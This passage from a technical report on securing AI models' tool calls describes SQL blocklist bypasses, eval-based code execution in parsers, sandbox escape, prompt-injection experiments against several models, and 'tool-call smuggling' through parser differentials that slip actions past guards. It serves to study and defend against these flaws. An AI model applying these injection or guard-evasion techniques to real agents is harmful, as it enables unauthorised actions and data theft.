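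SQL is harder to restrict in this way because useful queries use so much of the language. AWS's *CVE-2026-85787* (2026) describes an incomplete blocklist in the company's PostgreSQL server for MCP, which let queries change data in read-only mode. A few days later, AWS's *CVE-2026-87911* (2026) described another way past the same check, which could run operating-system commands on the database's host. It worked only if the assistant's account had the right to start programs, which a sales assistant never needs. Version 1.1.7 fixes both flaws, but AWS still calls an account with minimal privileges "the strongest control". Forkast gave similar advice in September 2026 about Postgres MCP Pro, which then had an unpatched flaw that allowed files on the server to be read in restricted mode.

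These failures all happen because the check runs outside the database and relies on a complete account of what each SQL feature can do. The database, by contrast, tests permissions when a query tries to use something. A check is still useful for problems that permissions don't cover, such as a query that would run for an hour.

### Giving the model a smaller language

An application can also avoid running general-purpose code altogether. LangChain's LLMMathChain component, which did calculations by having the model write Python and then running it, shows why this is appealing. Snyk's *Arbitrary Code Execution Affecting langchain package, versions [,0.0.142)* (2023) warned that a user could make the component run any code, including code that read the application's secret keys. LangChain fixed this in version 0.0.142.

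By version 0.0.245, the component relied on numexpr, a library for evaluating numerical expressions. Numexpr's evaluation function passed its text to Python's `eval`, as Wiz's *CVE-2023-39631* explains, so an attacker could again run code through a component meant only for calculation. According to GitLab's *CVE-2023-39631* (2023), LangChain responded by making numexpr optional in version 0.0.308. This kept the library out of applications that did not need it, but did not itself fix the evaluation function.

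A developer can limit the model to an approved list of database objects. In the SQL MCP Server (Microsoft, 2026), the developer lists the tables, views and stored procedures that each role may use. A stored procedure is a query saved in the database with gaps for values. If the model can only choose a procedure and fill in the gaps, the developer again controls the query's structure, and parameters protect the query as they do on an ordinary website.

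An assistant limited to predefined procedures can answer only the questions its developer anticipated. If it only has procedures for sales by region and by month, it cannot find customers who stopped buying after a price rise. Datadog Security Labs observes that companies often need more open-ended tools for their agents, which conflicts with this restriction. A sensible division is to use procedures for anything that changes data and to allow free queries only on restricted views.

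### Running the code in isolation

Some tasks, such as cleaning a spreadsheet or fitting a forecast, need a full programming language. The application can run the model's program for these tasks in a sandbox, an environment with its own files and no access to the machine that hosts the application. The program can still do anything Python allows, but only to what the sandbox contains.

Semantic Kernel ran the model's code in sandboxed cloud containers, and Microsoft found a way to escape them without exploiting a flaw in the containers themselves. Semantic Kernel had a function that copied files from the sandbox to the host. In the .NET version, a developer had accidentally marked this function as a tool for the model, which let the model choose where on the host each file went. Planted instructions could make the model write a program inside the sandbox and copy it to the host's Windows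 Startup folder, so that it would run when a user signed in. The function that copied files in the other direction could bring private keys from the host into the sandbox.

Microsoft fixed the first problem in version 1.71.0 by removing the function from the model's tools and checking the destination when the developer's own code calls it. The protection for uploads is off unless developers turn it on.

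The more strictly an application isolates the model's code, the less useful that code can be. A forecasting program needs sales figures, and may also need to download a library or return a chart. Each file or connection that the developer allows could also let an attacker in or data out. Isolation helps less with database queries, because they have to reach the company's data. Running a query on a copy of the database protects the original from deletion, but the query can still reveal confidential data such as salaries.

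The sales assistant could combine these methods. Its account could read only restricted views, the wrapper would accept one statement at a time and stop slow queries, and any Python would run in a sandbox that held the query's result and had no network connection. A misled model could still give a wrong answer, but it could not delete the sales records or look up a colleague's pay.

### Commands, templates and file paths

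The same mistake occurs wherever software interprets part of the model's output as an instruction. A shell, the program that interprets typed commands, treats certain characters as separators between commands. If a tool pastes the model's text into a command line, the text can add a second command. The tool can avoid this by starting the intended program directly, without a shell, and passing it the arguments as a list.

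Template engines, which build web pages on a server, evaluate expressions between special brackets. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe an application that used the model's answer as the template, so the engine evaluated any expressions in the answer. Those expressions could run commands on the server. The application should keep a fixed template and insert the answer as a value.

A file path can contain steps up to a parent folder, so a path that begins in a permitted folder may lead outside it. Semantic Kernel's new check converts the path to its full form before comparing it with the permitted folders.

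### Requests to internal servers

Company servers can often reach pages that outsiders cannot, such as an administration page that accepts requests only from the same machine. In server-side request forgery, an attacker gets the server to request such a page for them. If a model chooses which addresses a server fetches, an attacker can do this through the model.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian discussed eight classic web flaws in their August 2026 study but tested only server-side request forgery. They built TicketOracle, a concert website with an assistant whose only tool fetched any address it was given. An administration page on the same machine listed users' details and could delete accounts without asking for a login. In April 2026, they tried five attacks ten times each on each of seven models. In four attacks, the user asked for the internal address directly. In the fifth, the attacker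 hid the request in a concert review that the assistant read for another user.

| Model | Find open ports | Read user records | Change data | Change data, empty reply | Planted review | Planted review, rules in prompt |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 6 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 5 | 0 |
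| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The numbers are successes out of ten. Adding a list of permitted addresses to the prompt, with an order to refuse all others, stopped every direct attack, but the planted review succeeded against Llama more often than before. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian conclude that the rules made the attack on Llama stronger. However, they had also rewritten the review to claim that the list now included the internal address, so either change could explain the result.

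The ten attempts took place in a single conversation, so the model could see its earlier replies and may have repeated them. Ten successes or ten refusals are therefore weaker evidence than they would be from ten separate trials. The scoring may also understate the damage. Except when the reply was empty by design, an attempt counted as a success only if the assistant also reported the result, so an unreported deletion would have counted as a failure. The researchers did not try to refine their prompts against the models that refused.

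TicketOracle's code was equally insecure with all seven models, but a developer who switched from Claude to Llama would have gone from no successful attacks to many. The application can remove this dependence on the model by asking it for a concert's ID and building the address itself. If the application must accept whole addresses, it should reject those that lead to its own machine or a private network, and repeat the check after every redirect. A firewall can block the same destinations in case the check misses one, and the administration page should require a login even from the machine it runs on.

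## How generated text becomes a tool call

A model generates every tool call as text, even when the application asks only for a concert's ID. A separate program, the tool-call parser, searches that text for a call, converts the arguments into types such as numbers and lists, and returns an object the wrapper can use. The parser runs before the guard, so the guard cannot prevent damage that happens during parsing.

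### From tokens to an object

Suppose the office assistant has a tool called `find_documents`, which takes a search phrase and a maximum number of results. A call goes through five steps.

1. The software that runs the model adds the tool's declaration to the model's input, in a format the model learned in training.
2. The model writes a marker that opens a call, the tool's name, the arguments and a marker that closes the call.
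3. The parser finds the markers and separates the call from any text meant for the user.
4. It decodes the arguments and converts each one to the type given in the schema.
5. It returns an object with an ID, which the wrapper later uses to match the tool's result to the call.

If the user asks for twelve documents about the budget, the application might receive this:

```
{"id": "call_1",
 "type": "function",
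 "function": {"name": "find_documents",
              "arguments": "{\"phrase\": \"budget\", \"limit\": 12}"}}
```

Commercial providers convert generated text into tool calls on their own servers. Companies that run open models themselves use an inference server, a program that loads a model and answers requests over a network. vLLM, a widely used open-source inference server, has different parsers for different models because the format of tool calls varies between models.

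Some models write the arguments as JSON, and others write something like a line of Python. Qwen3-Coder, an open model for programming, uses tags like those in a web page. According to the documentation of EasyDeL, an open-source library for running models, one tag gives the function's name, and each argument is plain text between a pair of tags. The text has no quotation marks to distinguish the number 12 from the string "12", so the parser has to look up the argument's type in the schema.

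The first step can also go wrong. vLLM's *Chasing 100% Accuracy* traces failed tool calls by Kimi K2 to a missing prompt marker for the start of the model's turn. As a security measure, vLLM passes a setting to a model's prompt-formatting code only if that code declares it. Kimi K2's code did not declare the setting that adds the marker, so vLLM dropped the setting without an error and the model received a malformed prompt. Kimi's developers fixed the problem by declaring the setting.

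### When the parser runs the text as code

In 2025, vLLM's parser for Qwen3-Coder could run part of the model's output as Python code. The parser converted an argument's text to an integer if the schema listed it as one, and had similar rules for other common types. If it did not recognise the type, it passed the text to Python's `eval`, the function behind the Semantic Kernel flaw, presumably to turn text such as `[1, 2]` into a list.

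GitHub's *GHSA-79J6-G2M3-JGFW* (2025), the security advisory for this flaw, explains that any logged-in user could run code on the server by getting the model to pass that code as an argument. The server was vulnerable only if its operator had turned on tool calling and chosen this parser, and if the argument's type was missing or unrecognised. The flaw, CVE-2025-9141, affected vLLM from version 0.10.0, and version 0.10.1.1 fixed it.

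The advisory rates the flaw as high severity. Red Hat's *CVE-2025-9141* cites the need for a valid login as the reason it is not critical. That requirement offers less protection if a company puts a public chatbot in front of the server, because the chatbot has the login and its visitors can influence what the model writes. If one of the chatbot's tools had an argument with no declared type, a visitor might have been able to exploit the flaw without an account. A guard that denied the resulting tool call would have been too late, because the code would already have run.

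The parser came from a pull request by ranpox (2025). On the day the request was opened, before the flaw reached users, an automated reviewer from Google marked the `eval` call as a critical vulnerability. It recommended deleting the call, since the remaining code would then keep the value as a string. A maintainer merged the parser the same day "to unblock model usage". The advisory appeared 30 days later.

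A parser can handle lists safely with `ast.literal_eval`, a Python function that reads values such as numbers, strings and lists without running code. According to its documentation, vllm-mlx, a similar server for Apple computers, uses this function in its parser for a newer Qwen model. Few of the known flaws of this kind are in parsers. Ma, Rong and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Demystifying and Repairing LLM-in-the-Loop Vulnerabilities*, identified 41 vulnerabilities that an attacker can exploit only through a model. Three were in code that parses or dispatches the model's output, including the one described above, and 20 were in applications that run generated code or expressions.

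### Calls to tools the application did not offer

A parser can correctly convert a call to a tool that the application never offered. *Takedown* (Lee, Kim and colleagues, 2025) looked for this problem in eight coding agents, which are model-driven programs that edit files and run commands for a developer. The paper describes two places to check a tool's name. The provider's API can compare it with the tools listed in the request, and the agent can check it again before running anything.

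In September 2025 Lee and colleagues reported that Anthropic's API did not make this comparison, but the APIs for OpenAI's models, Gemini and Grok did. An attacker who got Claude to write a call in its usual format could therefore choose any tool name, and the API would return the call as if it were valid. This did harm only if the agent had code for that tool and ran it without checking the call itself. Lee and colleagues note that no standard makes either the provider or the agent responsible for the check, so each may rely on the other.

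Some agents don't use the provider's tool-calling feature. They instruct the model to write calls in a custom format, then search its output for them. Lee and colleagues got one such agent to create a file in read-only mode by having the model repeat text formatted as a call. The parser could not distinguish a call from a quoted one, and the agent did not check whether the tool was enabled. The code that runs a tool is still present after the tool is removed from the list the model receives.

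An attacker could make two of the eight agents run disabled tools. Lee and colleagues reported both flaws to the developers but did not name the agents because disclosure was still under way. Their paper mentions no fix for either flaw.

Anthropic has since let developers mark a tool as strict. According to its *Strict tool use* documentation, this guarantees that the name in a call will be one of the tools provided and that the arguments will match the schema. The feature entered public beta in November 2025 and became generally available in February 2026, according to Anthropic's *Structured outputs on the Claude Developer Platform* (2025). The documentation doesn't extend this guarantee to other tools, so anyone building an agent with them should assume that the API may still return an unknown name.

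Strict mode cannot cover every tool in a large agent. A request can include at most 20 strict tools, and Anthropic's tools for controlling a computer or browser do not support strict mode. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz surveyed 106 public MCP servers and counted 5,778 tools, about 55 per server on average, so a single server could exceed the limit. Checking the tool name in a call against the currently enabled tools takes the agent one lookup and works with any provider.

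### When software completes an unfinished call

A tool call may stop partway because the connection fails or the response reaches the developer's token limit. Some parsers then fill in what is missing. The parser in vllm-mlx, for instance, adds closing tags when the output ends mid-call.

Completing a call in this way can change its meaning. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz cut JSON arguments short at ten points and gave the pieces to six parsers. One cut split the number 12, so the unfinished object ended with a count of 1. LangChain's parser for partial JSON closed the object and returned a count of 1 instead of 12. Another framework, which the paper does not name because a report to its developers is still open, passed on the unfinished text as a string. Python's strict JSON parser and two Go parsers rejected it. The paper mentions no change to LangChain's parser, which is designed to complete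 partial JSON.

Truncated numbers are especially easy to misread because numbers have no closing mark. If a call to delete files older than 365 days is cut off after the first digit, the tool would delete everything older than 3 days. A string ends with a quotation mark, so a parser can tell when one is unfinished. But if the parser adds the missing mark, the path `/reports/2024/drafts` could become `/reports`.

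A partial parser is useful for showing progress, such as displaying a document as the model writes it. But a tool that runs on partial output may take an action that cannot be undone when the rest arrives.

### When streaming changes the call

Even a complete call can change if the parser sends it in pieces. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz tested vLLM 0.32.0's parser for Python-style calls, running it outside the server. The test call named the `path` argument twice, first as `report.pdf` and then as `../secrets.env`. The parser kept the second path when it read the whole call at once, but when it read the call as a stream, it produced `report.pdf.env`, which appears nowhere in the input.

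To stream a call, this parser repeatedly converts what it has read so far into JSON and sends the part it has not sent before. In the test, it had already sent the ten characters of `report.pdf` when the second path, `../secrets.env`, replaced the first. The parser skipped the first ten characters of the new path and sent only `.env`, which the receiver added to the path it already had, producing `report.pdf.env`.

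Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz did not report this behaviour to vLLM, and they describe no fix. No model in their tests repeated an argument in the calls whose raw text they could read, and an attacker who can insert a repeated argument in transit already controls the call. The attack is therefore weak, but it shows that a parser tested on complete text may produce a different result when the text is streamed.

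A similar error can arise without an attacker. If Qwen3-Coder leaves out the tag that closes a string argument, vLLM's streaming parser could include the start of the next argument in that string, according to ec-jt (2026), in *[Tool Parser] Qwen3Coder*. This pull request would make the parser end the string where the next argument begins, but vLLM had not merged it, so the flaw may remain.

### Why the guard has to wait for the whole call

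A streaming output filter has to check unfinished text, but a tool call has no effect until the executor runs it. The guard can therefore wait until the streamed arguments are complete before checking them, as Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz recommend.

A guard that decides before a whole tool call has arrived can be wrong even if every piece arrives intact. An email address that reads `dana@firm.co` partway through may end as `dana@firm.co.example`, which belongs to a different domain. Later arguments can also change what a call does. Anthropic's *Structured outputs* notes that required fields come before optional ones in its structured output. A guard that decided as soon as it had an email's recipient and body could therefore miss an optional field that adds an attachment.

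By default, Anthropic's API validates each complete argument before streaming it. Anthropic's *Fine-grained tool streaming* describes a faster option that sends fragments immediately, without validation, so the combined text may not be valid JSON. In both cases, the application should join the fragments and parse them only when it receives the event that marks the end of the call. It should also check the stop reason field to see why the model stopped writing. If the JSON is invalid, the application should return an error to the model instead of running the tool.

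Anthropic's advice on tool calls cut off by the token limit is less consistent. The streaming guide says the developer can either repeat the request with a higher limit or repair the partial input, but Anthropic's *Stop reasons and fallback* says the developer needs to repeat the request. Repeating it is safer for any tool that changes something, because a repaired call contains a guess about what the model would have written.

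### What strict mode guarantees

A strict mode prevents many malformed calls by restricting the model while it writes. The provider converts the tool's schema into a grammar, which is a set of rules that determines which tokens may come next. At each step the software sets the probability of every other token to zero, much as memorization-free decoding does with forbidden passages, and rescales the rest. If *p*(*t*) is the model's probability for token *t* and *A* is the set of allowed tokens, the new probability of an allowed token is

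*p*′(*t*) = *p*(*t*) / Σ *p*(*u*), summed over all *u* in *A*.

Suppose the model has reached the value of `limit`, which must be an integer. It gives a probability of 0.5 to a quotation mark, which would begin a string such as "twelve", 0.3 to the digit 1 and 0.2 to the digit 2. The grammar rules out the quotation mark, so the digits' probabilities become 0.3 / 0.5 = 0.6 and 0.2 / 0.5 = 0.4. The model has to write a number even if the user never gave one.

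Strict mode can also make calls more complete. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz had six commercial models call a tool with an optional field that had a default value, 40 times each. In the providers' ordinary modes, five of the six models omitted the field every time. In OpenAI's strict mode, the only strict mode they tested, no call omitted it. A missing field matters when its default affects the action. For example, if a call to delete a folder omits the field for whether the deletion is permanent, the guard and the executor may fill in different defaults.

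Anthropic's strict mode allows up to 24 optional fields across all the strict schemas in a request, so it does not by itself guarantee that a call includes every field. Each optional field roughly doubles part of the grammar, so Anthropic limits their number and suggests making fields required where possible. A developer who follows this advice also gets calls in which every value is explicit.

Anthropic lists several cases where its models' output may not match the schema. A refusal takes precedence over the required format, and a response that reaches the token limit may stop in the middle of a call. A value chosen from a fixed list may be capitalised differently from the list entry, and the API gives no error when this happens. Anthropic therefore recommends ignoring case when comparing such values.

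The grammar also cannot express every rule in a schema. If a refund tool has a maximum refund of 100, Anthropic's API rejects a strict schema that states this limit. Most of Anthropic's helper libraries can move the limit into the field's description, where the model can read it but the grammar does not enforce it. Some of these libraries also check the response against the original limit. Otherwise, the developer has to write that check, or the tool may receive a correctly formatted request to refund 5,000.

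A call can match the schema and still be unauthorised. If planted text causes the model to email a stranger, strict mode ensures only that the request is well formed. It also can't stop a gateway from changing the call later, or a tool server from supplying a misleading schema.

### Which component should check what

The checks depend on different information, so no single component can do them all. The provider has the model's raw output but usually doesn't have the company's rules. The guard has those rules but receives the call only after other software has parsed it.

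| Component | What to check |
|---|---|
| Provider's API or inference server | The call is complete, its tool was in the request, and its arguments have the declared types |
| Wrapper | The response ended normally, the tool is enabled for this user and session, and the arguments respect limits that the grammar cannot express |
| Guard | This user may take this action with these values |
| Executor | The call is the one the guard approved, and the tool's own account has permission to carry it out |

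The wrapper should repeat the provider's checks on names and types, because a developer may switch to a provider that checks less, and a gateway may have altered the call in transit. The wrapper should also reject arguments the schema does not declare. When a tool call fails one of these checks, the wrapper should discard it and ask the model for a new one rather than guess what was meant, as a parser reasonably can when a bracket is missing from ordinary text.

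## When the check and the tool read the same call differently

A guard can apply the right rule to a complete, well-formed tool call and still approve a different action from the one that runs, because the executor parses the call again and may interpret it differently. In November 2026, Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz named the deliberate use of this mismatch "tool-call smuggling".

### One cancellation, two readings

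The main example comes from τ-bench, a public set of customer-service tasks for agents. A customer asks an airline's agent to cancel reservation I3EHXC, and the model writes a correct call. The call passes through a gateway that an attacker controls before it reaches the guard.

1. The gateway puts another customer's reservation, U86B6B, in the field `reservation_id`. It then adds the same field name again with different capital letters, and puts I3EHXC there.
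2. The guard uses the standard JSON decoder of the programming language Go, which ignores capitals in field names and keeps the last match. It finds I3EHXC, confirms that the customer owns it, and approves and logs the call.
3. The executor, built with one of the official MCP software development kits (SDKs), accepts only the exact field name. It finds U86B6B, cancels that reservation and refunds its $1,203.

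The log shows an approved cancellation of I3EHXC, so someone reviewing the log later would find nothing wrong. Testing the guard alone would not reveal the problem either. When the researchers put each reservation number in an ordinary call, the guard allowed the customer's own reservation and denied the other.

If the gateway had replaced one number with the other, the guard would have denied the call. The second field gets the call past the guard, but only for an attacker who can already alter calls in transit. The researchers also gave the altered text directly to the guard instead of breaking into a real gateway, and they wrote the ownership rule themselves. The Go decoder was real and ran with its default settings.

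The benchmark's cancellation tool checked only that the reservation existed. If it had compared the reservation's owner with the customer's login, it would have refused to cancel U86B6B whatever the guard had read.

### The same flaw in web servers

The attack is named after HTTP request smuggling, which Segal (2005) announced on a security mailing list in *A new whitepaper by Watchfire*. Large websites often have a front-end server that receives all requests and passes them to a back-end server over a shared connection. HTTP/1.1, an old but still common version of the web's protocol, has no separator between requests, so each server has to work out where a request ends.

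A request can give its length as a total number of bytes, or arrive in pieces, each labeled with its size. If a request does both and the two lengths conflict, the front end might count 60 bytes while the back end stops after 40. The back end then treats the remaining 20 bytes as the start of the next visitor's request. An attacker can use those bytes to get a request past the front end's checks or to change what another visitor's request does.

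Developers have been fixing individual servers ever since. In *HTTP/1.1 must die*, Kettle described a flaw of this kind inside Cloudflare's network that exposed more than 24 million websites in 2025. Cloudflare patched it within hours, but Kettle argues that such repairs will never end the problem, because the HTTP/1.1 format allows two readings of the same message. HTTP/2 builds each message's length into the format, which nearly eliminates the attack if the front end also uses HTTP/2 to reach the back end. In *Can AI do novel security research?*, Kettle (2026) reported that an automated system had found roughly 700 vulnerable targets while testing 30,000 websites.

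### Where the two readings come from

JSON leaves similar choices to each program. Its standard says that the names in an object "SHOULD be unique", which is strong advice but not a requirement. A program that finds a repeated name can keep the first value, keep the last or reject the text. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz looked for such choices at every step between the text of a call and the resulting action.

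| Feature of the call | What one component does | What another does |
|---|---|---|
| A repeated field name | Keeps the first value | Keeps the last value |
| Two names that differ only in capitals | Treats them as one field | Treats them as two |
| A number in quotation marks | Converts it to a number | Rejects it |
| A letter written as a numeric code | Searches the text without decoding it | Decodes the letter |
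| A field the schema does not declare | Ignores it | Passes it to the tool |
| A missing field with a default value | Leaves it out | Fills it in |
| Several calls in one response | Matches approvals by position | Matches them by ID |

Unfinished calls are another source, since some parsers complete them and others reject them.

Many programs store every number in a format that is exact for whole numbers only up to 2⁵³, or 9,007,199,254,740,992. Such a program rounds the account number 9,007,199,254,740,993 down to 9,007,199,254,740,992. If the guard rounds and the executor doesn't, the guard checks a different account from the one the executor acts on.

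A large number can also keep a call from reaching the policy at all. *One Policy, Four Interception Points* (Shaw, 2026) tests Oathpost, a system Shaw built to apply one policy to an agent's actions at four places. The policy limited a search to 100 results, and the test call asked for 10³⁰. Three of the four components sent the call to the policy service, which denied it. The fourth, which checks a coding agent's tool calls, could not convert the number into a form it could send, so it never sent the call to the policy service.

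If the operator had set the component to block calls when the check fails, it refused the call but recorded no decision. Under the default setting, it did not stop the call and only added one to a counter of missing records. Shaw notes that this was not a parser differential, because the component failed before anything else read the number. But the defect is easier to exploit than the airline attack, since the model only has to write a large integer. Shaw found it in a development version, 0.1.0-dev.

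A different mismatch arises because JSON lets a writer replace any letter with a numeric code. Every parser the researchers tested decoded these codes the same way, but a filter that searches the raw text does not decode them. In one test, a data-loss filter blocked any call whose text contained the word "credentials". The attacker wrote one letter of that word as a code, so the filter found no match, and the executor created a file called `credentials.txt` with a secret in it. The same filter blocked the call when it checked the parsed file name.

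An undeclared field can reach a tool even when all the parsers agree. The researchers built a tool that assembled a shell command from its arguments, and a guard that looked for dangerous characters in the one field meant to hold outside text. They put a second command in a field missing from the schema. The schema allowed extra fields, the guard did not inspect this one, and the shell ran the command. The official MCP SDKs drop undeclared fields, so the attack needs a component between the guard and the tool to forward every field. The researchers wrote that component themselves, copying behaviour they had seen in the source code of real gateways.

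Call IDs matter when a model requests several actions at once. Suppose a response contains a call to read a file and a call to delete one, and an attacker swaps their IDs. A guard that approves calls by position allows the read and denies the delete. An executor that looks up the approved call by ID then finds the delete and runs it. The researchers tried six arrangements of IDs with three common lookup methods, and the denied delete ran in 10 of the 18 combinations. They wrote the lookup code themselves, so the test shows that the mistake is easy to make, but not that any particular product makes it.

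### How often components disagree

Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz fed identical text to eleven configurations of real parsers and compared the results. In 43 of the 55 possible pairs, the two parsers read at least one repeated or disguised field name differently. This is not an estimate of how many agents are vulnerable, because the eleven included three configurations of Python's parser and two versions of one Go library, and the researchers designed the 22 test inputs to cause disagreement. On ordinary calls, both parsers in every pair gave the same result.

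Two official MCP SDKs gave different results on 21 of the 22 type-conversion inputs that at least one of them accepted. But 20 of the inputs were very large integers, which one SDK accepted and the other rejected, so the count mostly reflects a single difference. That difference usually causes a call to fail rather than the wrong call to run. The two SDKs agreed on all 22 inputs with repeated or disguised names.

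Components also disagree when there is no attacker. Of the 4,693 distinct schemas the researchers found on the public tool servers they surveyed, 558 (11.9%) led to different results in different components. For 17 of these, validators disagreed about whether the schema itself was valid. For the other 541, the tool received different arguments depending on whether a component filled in default values. Many of those defaults, such as a page size, are probably harmless, but the difference matters when the guard's decision depends on the value.

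The official SDKs also leave out some of the checks that the MCP specification requires. *MCPGuard* (Sun, Liu and colleagues, 2026) compared the specification with two SDKs and confirmed 13 gaps in the Python SDK and 19 in the TypeScript SDK. For example, the specification limits one priority setting to numbers from 0 to 1, but the Python SDK accepted 1001. Both SDKs had passed all 42 applicable checks in the official test suite, which tests a running server from outside. Sun and colleagues reported the gaps privately to the maintainers. Developers who write a guard may leave out a limit because they assume the SDK already enforces it.

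### What an attacker can do with only a document

Someone who can edit the office assistant's shared document is in a much weaker position than someone who controls a gateway, because the model first has to reproduce an ambiguous field name in its tool call.

Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz gave ten models a document that asked them to copy a set of values exactly, with 25 trials per model. The values included repeated names, names with altered capitals and names ending in an invisible character. No model put any of these into the structure of its next tool call. For seven models, the researchers received the call only after other software had parsed it, which would have removed a repeated name, so the evidence about repeated names comes from the other three models, which wrote none in 75 trials, and from 120 further trials that asked for both copies.

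In a repeat of the attack on the file filter, a model wrote the call. Of 100 calls that contained the attacker's file name, the filter denied the 72 that spelled it plainly. The other 28 passed, but most contained the coded letter as ordinary characters that a parser does not decode, so the executor created a harmless file with a backslash in its name. None of the 100 created the blocked file.

The models stopped less of the ambiguous text when it belonged inside an argument. Some tools accept a string that itself contains JSON, such as a block of settings, and the server parses that string later. When asked to copy a settings object into such a string, the models kept names with altered capitals in 82 of 84 calls. When the strings were replayed through a Python guard and a Go executor, the guard approved a harmless setting and the executor used the attacker's in all 82 cases. The coded file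 name survived in 72 of 84 calls and got past the text filter.

This attack is the most worrying result for ordinary users because it needs no access to the connection, but few tools are open to it. Of the 5,778 tools surveyed, 24 had descriptions that mentioned an argument containing JSON text. The researchers also ran the guard and executor in their own test programs, not in a live product.

A model's resistance to planted instructions does not predict whether it will copy dangerous text. The open model Qwen3.8-27B never obeyed a planted instruction to change an action to "delete", but it copied a disguised version of the word into its arguments in 19 of 25 trials. Llama-3.3-70B obeyed the instruction every time and never copied the disguised word. A developer who tests only for obedience would therefore misjudge both models' risk of copying such text.

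### A tool server that adds a field

The attacker may instead run a tool server that the user has attached to the assistant. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz imitated the official MCP tool for reading text files. Their server copied its name and public schema but added one required field, `encoding`. A shared note, which the model also read, gave a format for that field that included the user's workstation name.

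The user's request mentioned the workstation, and the model used it to fill in the field. The guard looked up the approved schema by the tool's name. That schema declared only the file path and allowed extra fields, so the guard checked the path, approved the call and logged nothing else. The attacker's server received the workstation name in 29 of 30 trials across GPT-5.5, Claude Opus 5.5 and Qwen3.8-27B.

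In those trials the user had told the model to follow the note's requirements exactly. With more neutral requests, the name still leaked in 23 of 30 trials. Without the note, the models entered an ordinary text encoding in the field in 24 of 25 trials and never entered the name. A similar attack on ten airline and shop tools obtained the user's email address in 133 of 150 attempts, and Anthropic's classifier stopped the other 17.

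The guard and the attacker's server parsed the call identically here and differed only in which schema they used, so a better parser would not have helped. When the researchers made the approved schemas stricter by forbidding undeclared fields, the guard denied every call that carried the extra field. None of the 106 servers in their survey forbade extra fields at the top level, so a company has to add that restriction when it approves a tool.

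Ten trials per model on one prompt cannot give a precise success rate for other tools or wordings. They do show that the attack doesn't depend on a quirk of one model, and developers train models to fill in required fields.

### How one fix moved the disagreement

Parser differentials had already been found in released MCP software. GitHub's *MCP Go SDK Vulnerable to Improper Handling of Case Sensitivity* (2026) describes one, CVE-2026-27896, published in February. The official Go SDK read messages with Go's standard decoder, so it accepted `Method` where the protocol requires `method`. A proxy that looked for the exact name could miss a message that the SDK would then act on. The US National Vulnerability Database's *CVE-2026-27896 Detail* classes the flaw as an "Interpretation Conflict".

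The maintainers fixed the flaw in version 1.3.1 by switching to another decoder, segmentio/encoding, which is case-sensitive. Three weeks later GitHub (2026) published a second advisory, GHSA-q382-vc8q-7jhj. The new decoder ignored an invisible null character at the end of a field name. An attacker could add a second copy of a field with that character attached to its name, and the SDK would use the copy's value instead of the original's. A proxy that compared exact names would again treat the two as different fields. Version 1.4.1 fixes this with a corrected decoder.

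Francesco Lacerenza of the security firm Doyensec found both flaws. Each change was reasonable, but the maintainers had replaced one decoder's behavior with another's. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz confirmed that the corrected decoder no longer has the problem with null characters, although it still reads some of their inputs differently from other parsers.

A flaw in Envoy AI Gateway, which routes calls between agents and tool servers, was worse in one respect, because the gateway rewrote an ambiguous call as well as misreading it (GitHub, *Envoy AI Proxy*, 2026). In Doyensec's demonstration, a proxy in front of the gateway checked the tool's exact name, found a harmless greeting tool and logged the call as allowed. The gateway ignored capitals and took the name of a restricted tool from a second field. It then wrote a new, well-formed message that named only the restricted tool, and the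 tool server ran it.

The server could not have detected the attack, because the message it received was no longer ambiguous. The attacker did not need to control the connection, since any client that the first proxy allowed to call the greeting tool could send the ambiguous message. In a company that gives different employees or agents access to different tools, such a client is a more likely attacker than a compromised gateway. Version 0.6.0, released by May 2026, fixes the flaw.

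More such cases are coming. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz sent nine private reports to eight projects, and three of the affected products treat capital letters differently when checking a call than when acting on it. They withhold the names of components whose reports are still open.

A parser can also refuse ambiguous text. By default, version 2 of Go's JSON package rejects repeated names and treats names that differ only in capitalization as different. When the researchers also set it to refuse unknown fields, it rejected all 22 of their inputs with repeated or disguised names. These settings should rarely block ordinary calls, because the models they tested did not write such names in them. Strict parsing does not fix the other sources of disagreement, including filters that search raw text.

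### Why four of the five defences failed

Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz tested five defences, each against an attacker who knew how it worked. One was a provider's strict mode, which cannot affect what a gateway later does to the call. They ran the other four against nine crafted calls: six with repeated names, two with a null character in a name, and one with a coded letter.

| Defence | Crafted calls that got through, out of nine |
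|---|---|
| None | 9 |
| Validate the call against its schema | 9 |
| Parse and check the call, then forward the original text | 9 |
| Compare two settings of Python's parser | 3 |
| Compare Python's parser with segmentio/encoding 0.5.3 | 1 |
| Shared parse | 0 |

Schema validation failed because the validator also checks only one parse of the call. If that parse is valid, the guard approves the call, but the executor then parses the original text itself, possibly with a different result. Careful parsing at the guard fails for the same reason if the guard then forwards the text it received. A digital signature on that text would not help, because the text does not change between the guard and the executor.

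Comparing two parsers exposes an attack only if one of them reads the call as the executor does. Two settings of Python's parser, one that keeps the first copy of a name and one that keeps the last, give different results for a repeated name and so expose it. Both settings treat a name with a null character as a separate field, so their results match and the comparison misses the attack. Adding the older segmentio decoder, which ignores that character, exposes it. Neither pair detected the coded letter, because all the parsers decode it and only the text filter does not.

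Shaw found a similar limit in Oathpost, which evaluates every policy with two separate engines and makes no decision when their results differ. The engines share some helper code. When Shaw introduced small errors into the software, five errors in the shared code changed both engines' results in the same way. Only a test with a written expected answer caught them.

### Parsing the call once

In a shared parse, the software turns the original text into a call only once, and both the guard and the executor use the result. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz built a version of this.

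1. It parses the call, including any string argument that the approved schema marks as JSON text.
2. It keeps only the fields in the approved schema, at every level, and fills in default values.
3. The guard checks the resulting object.
4. The executor runs that same object.

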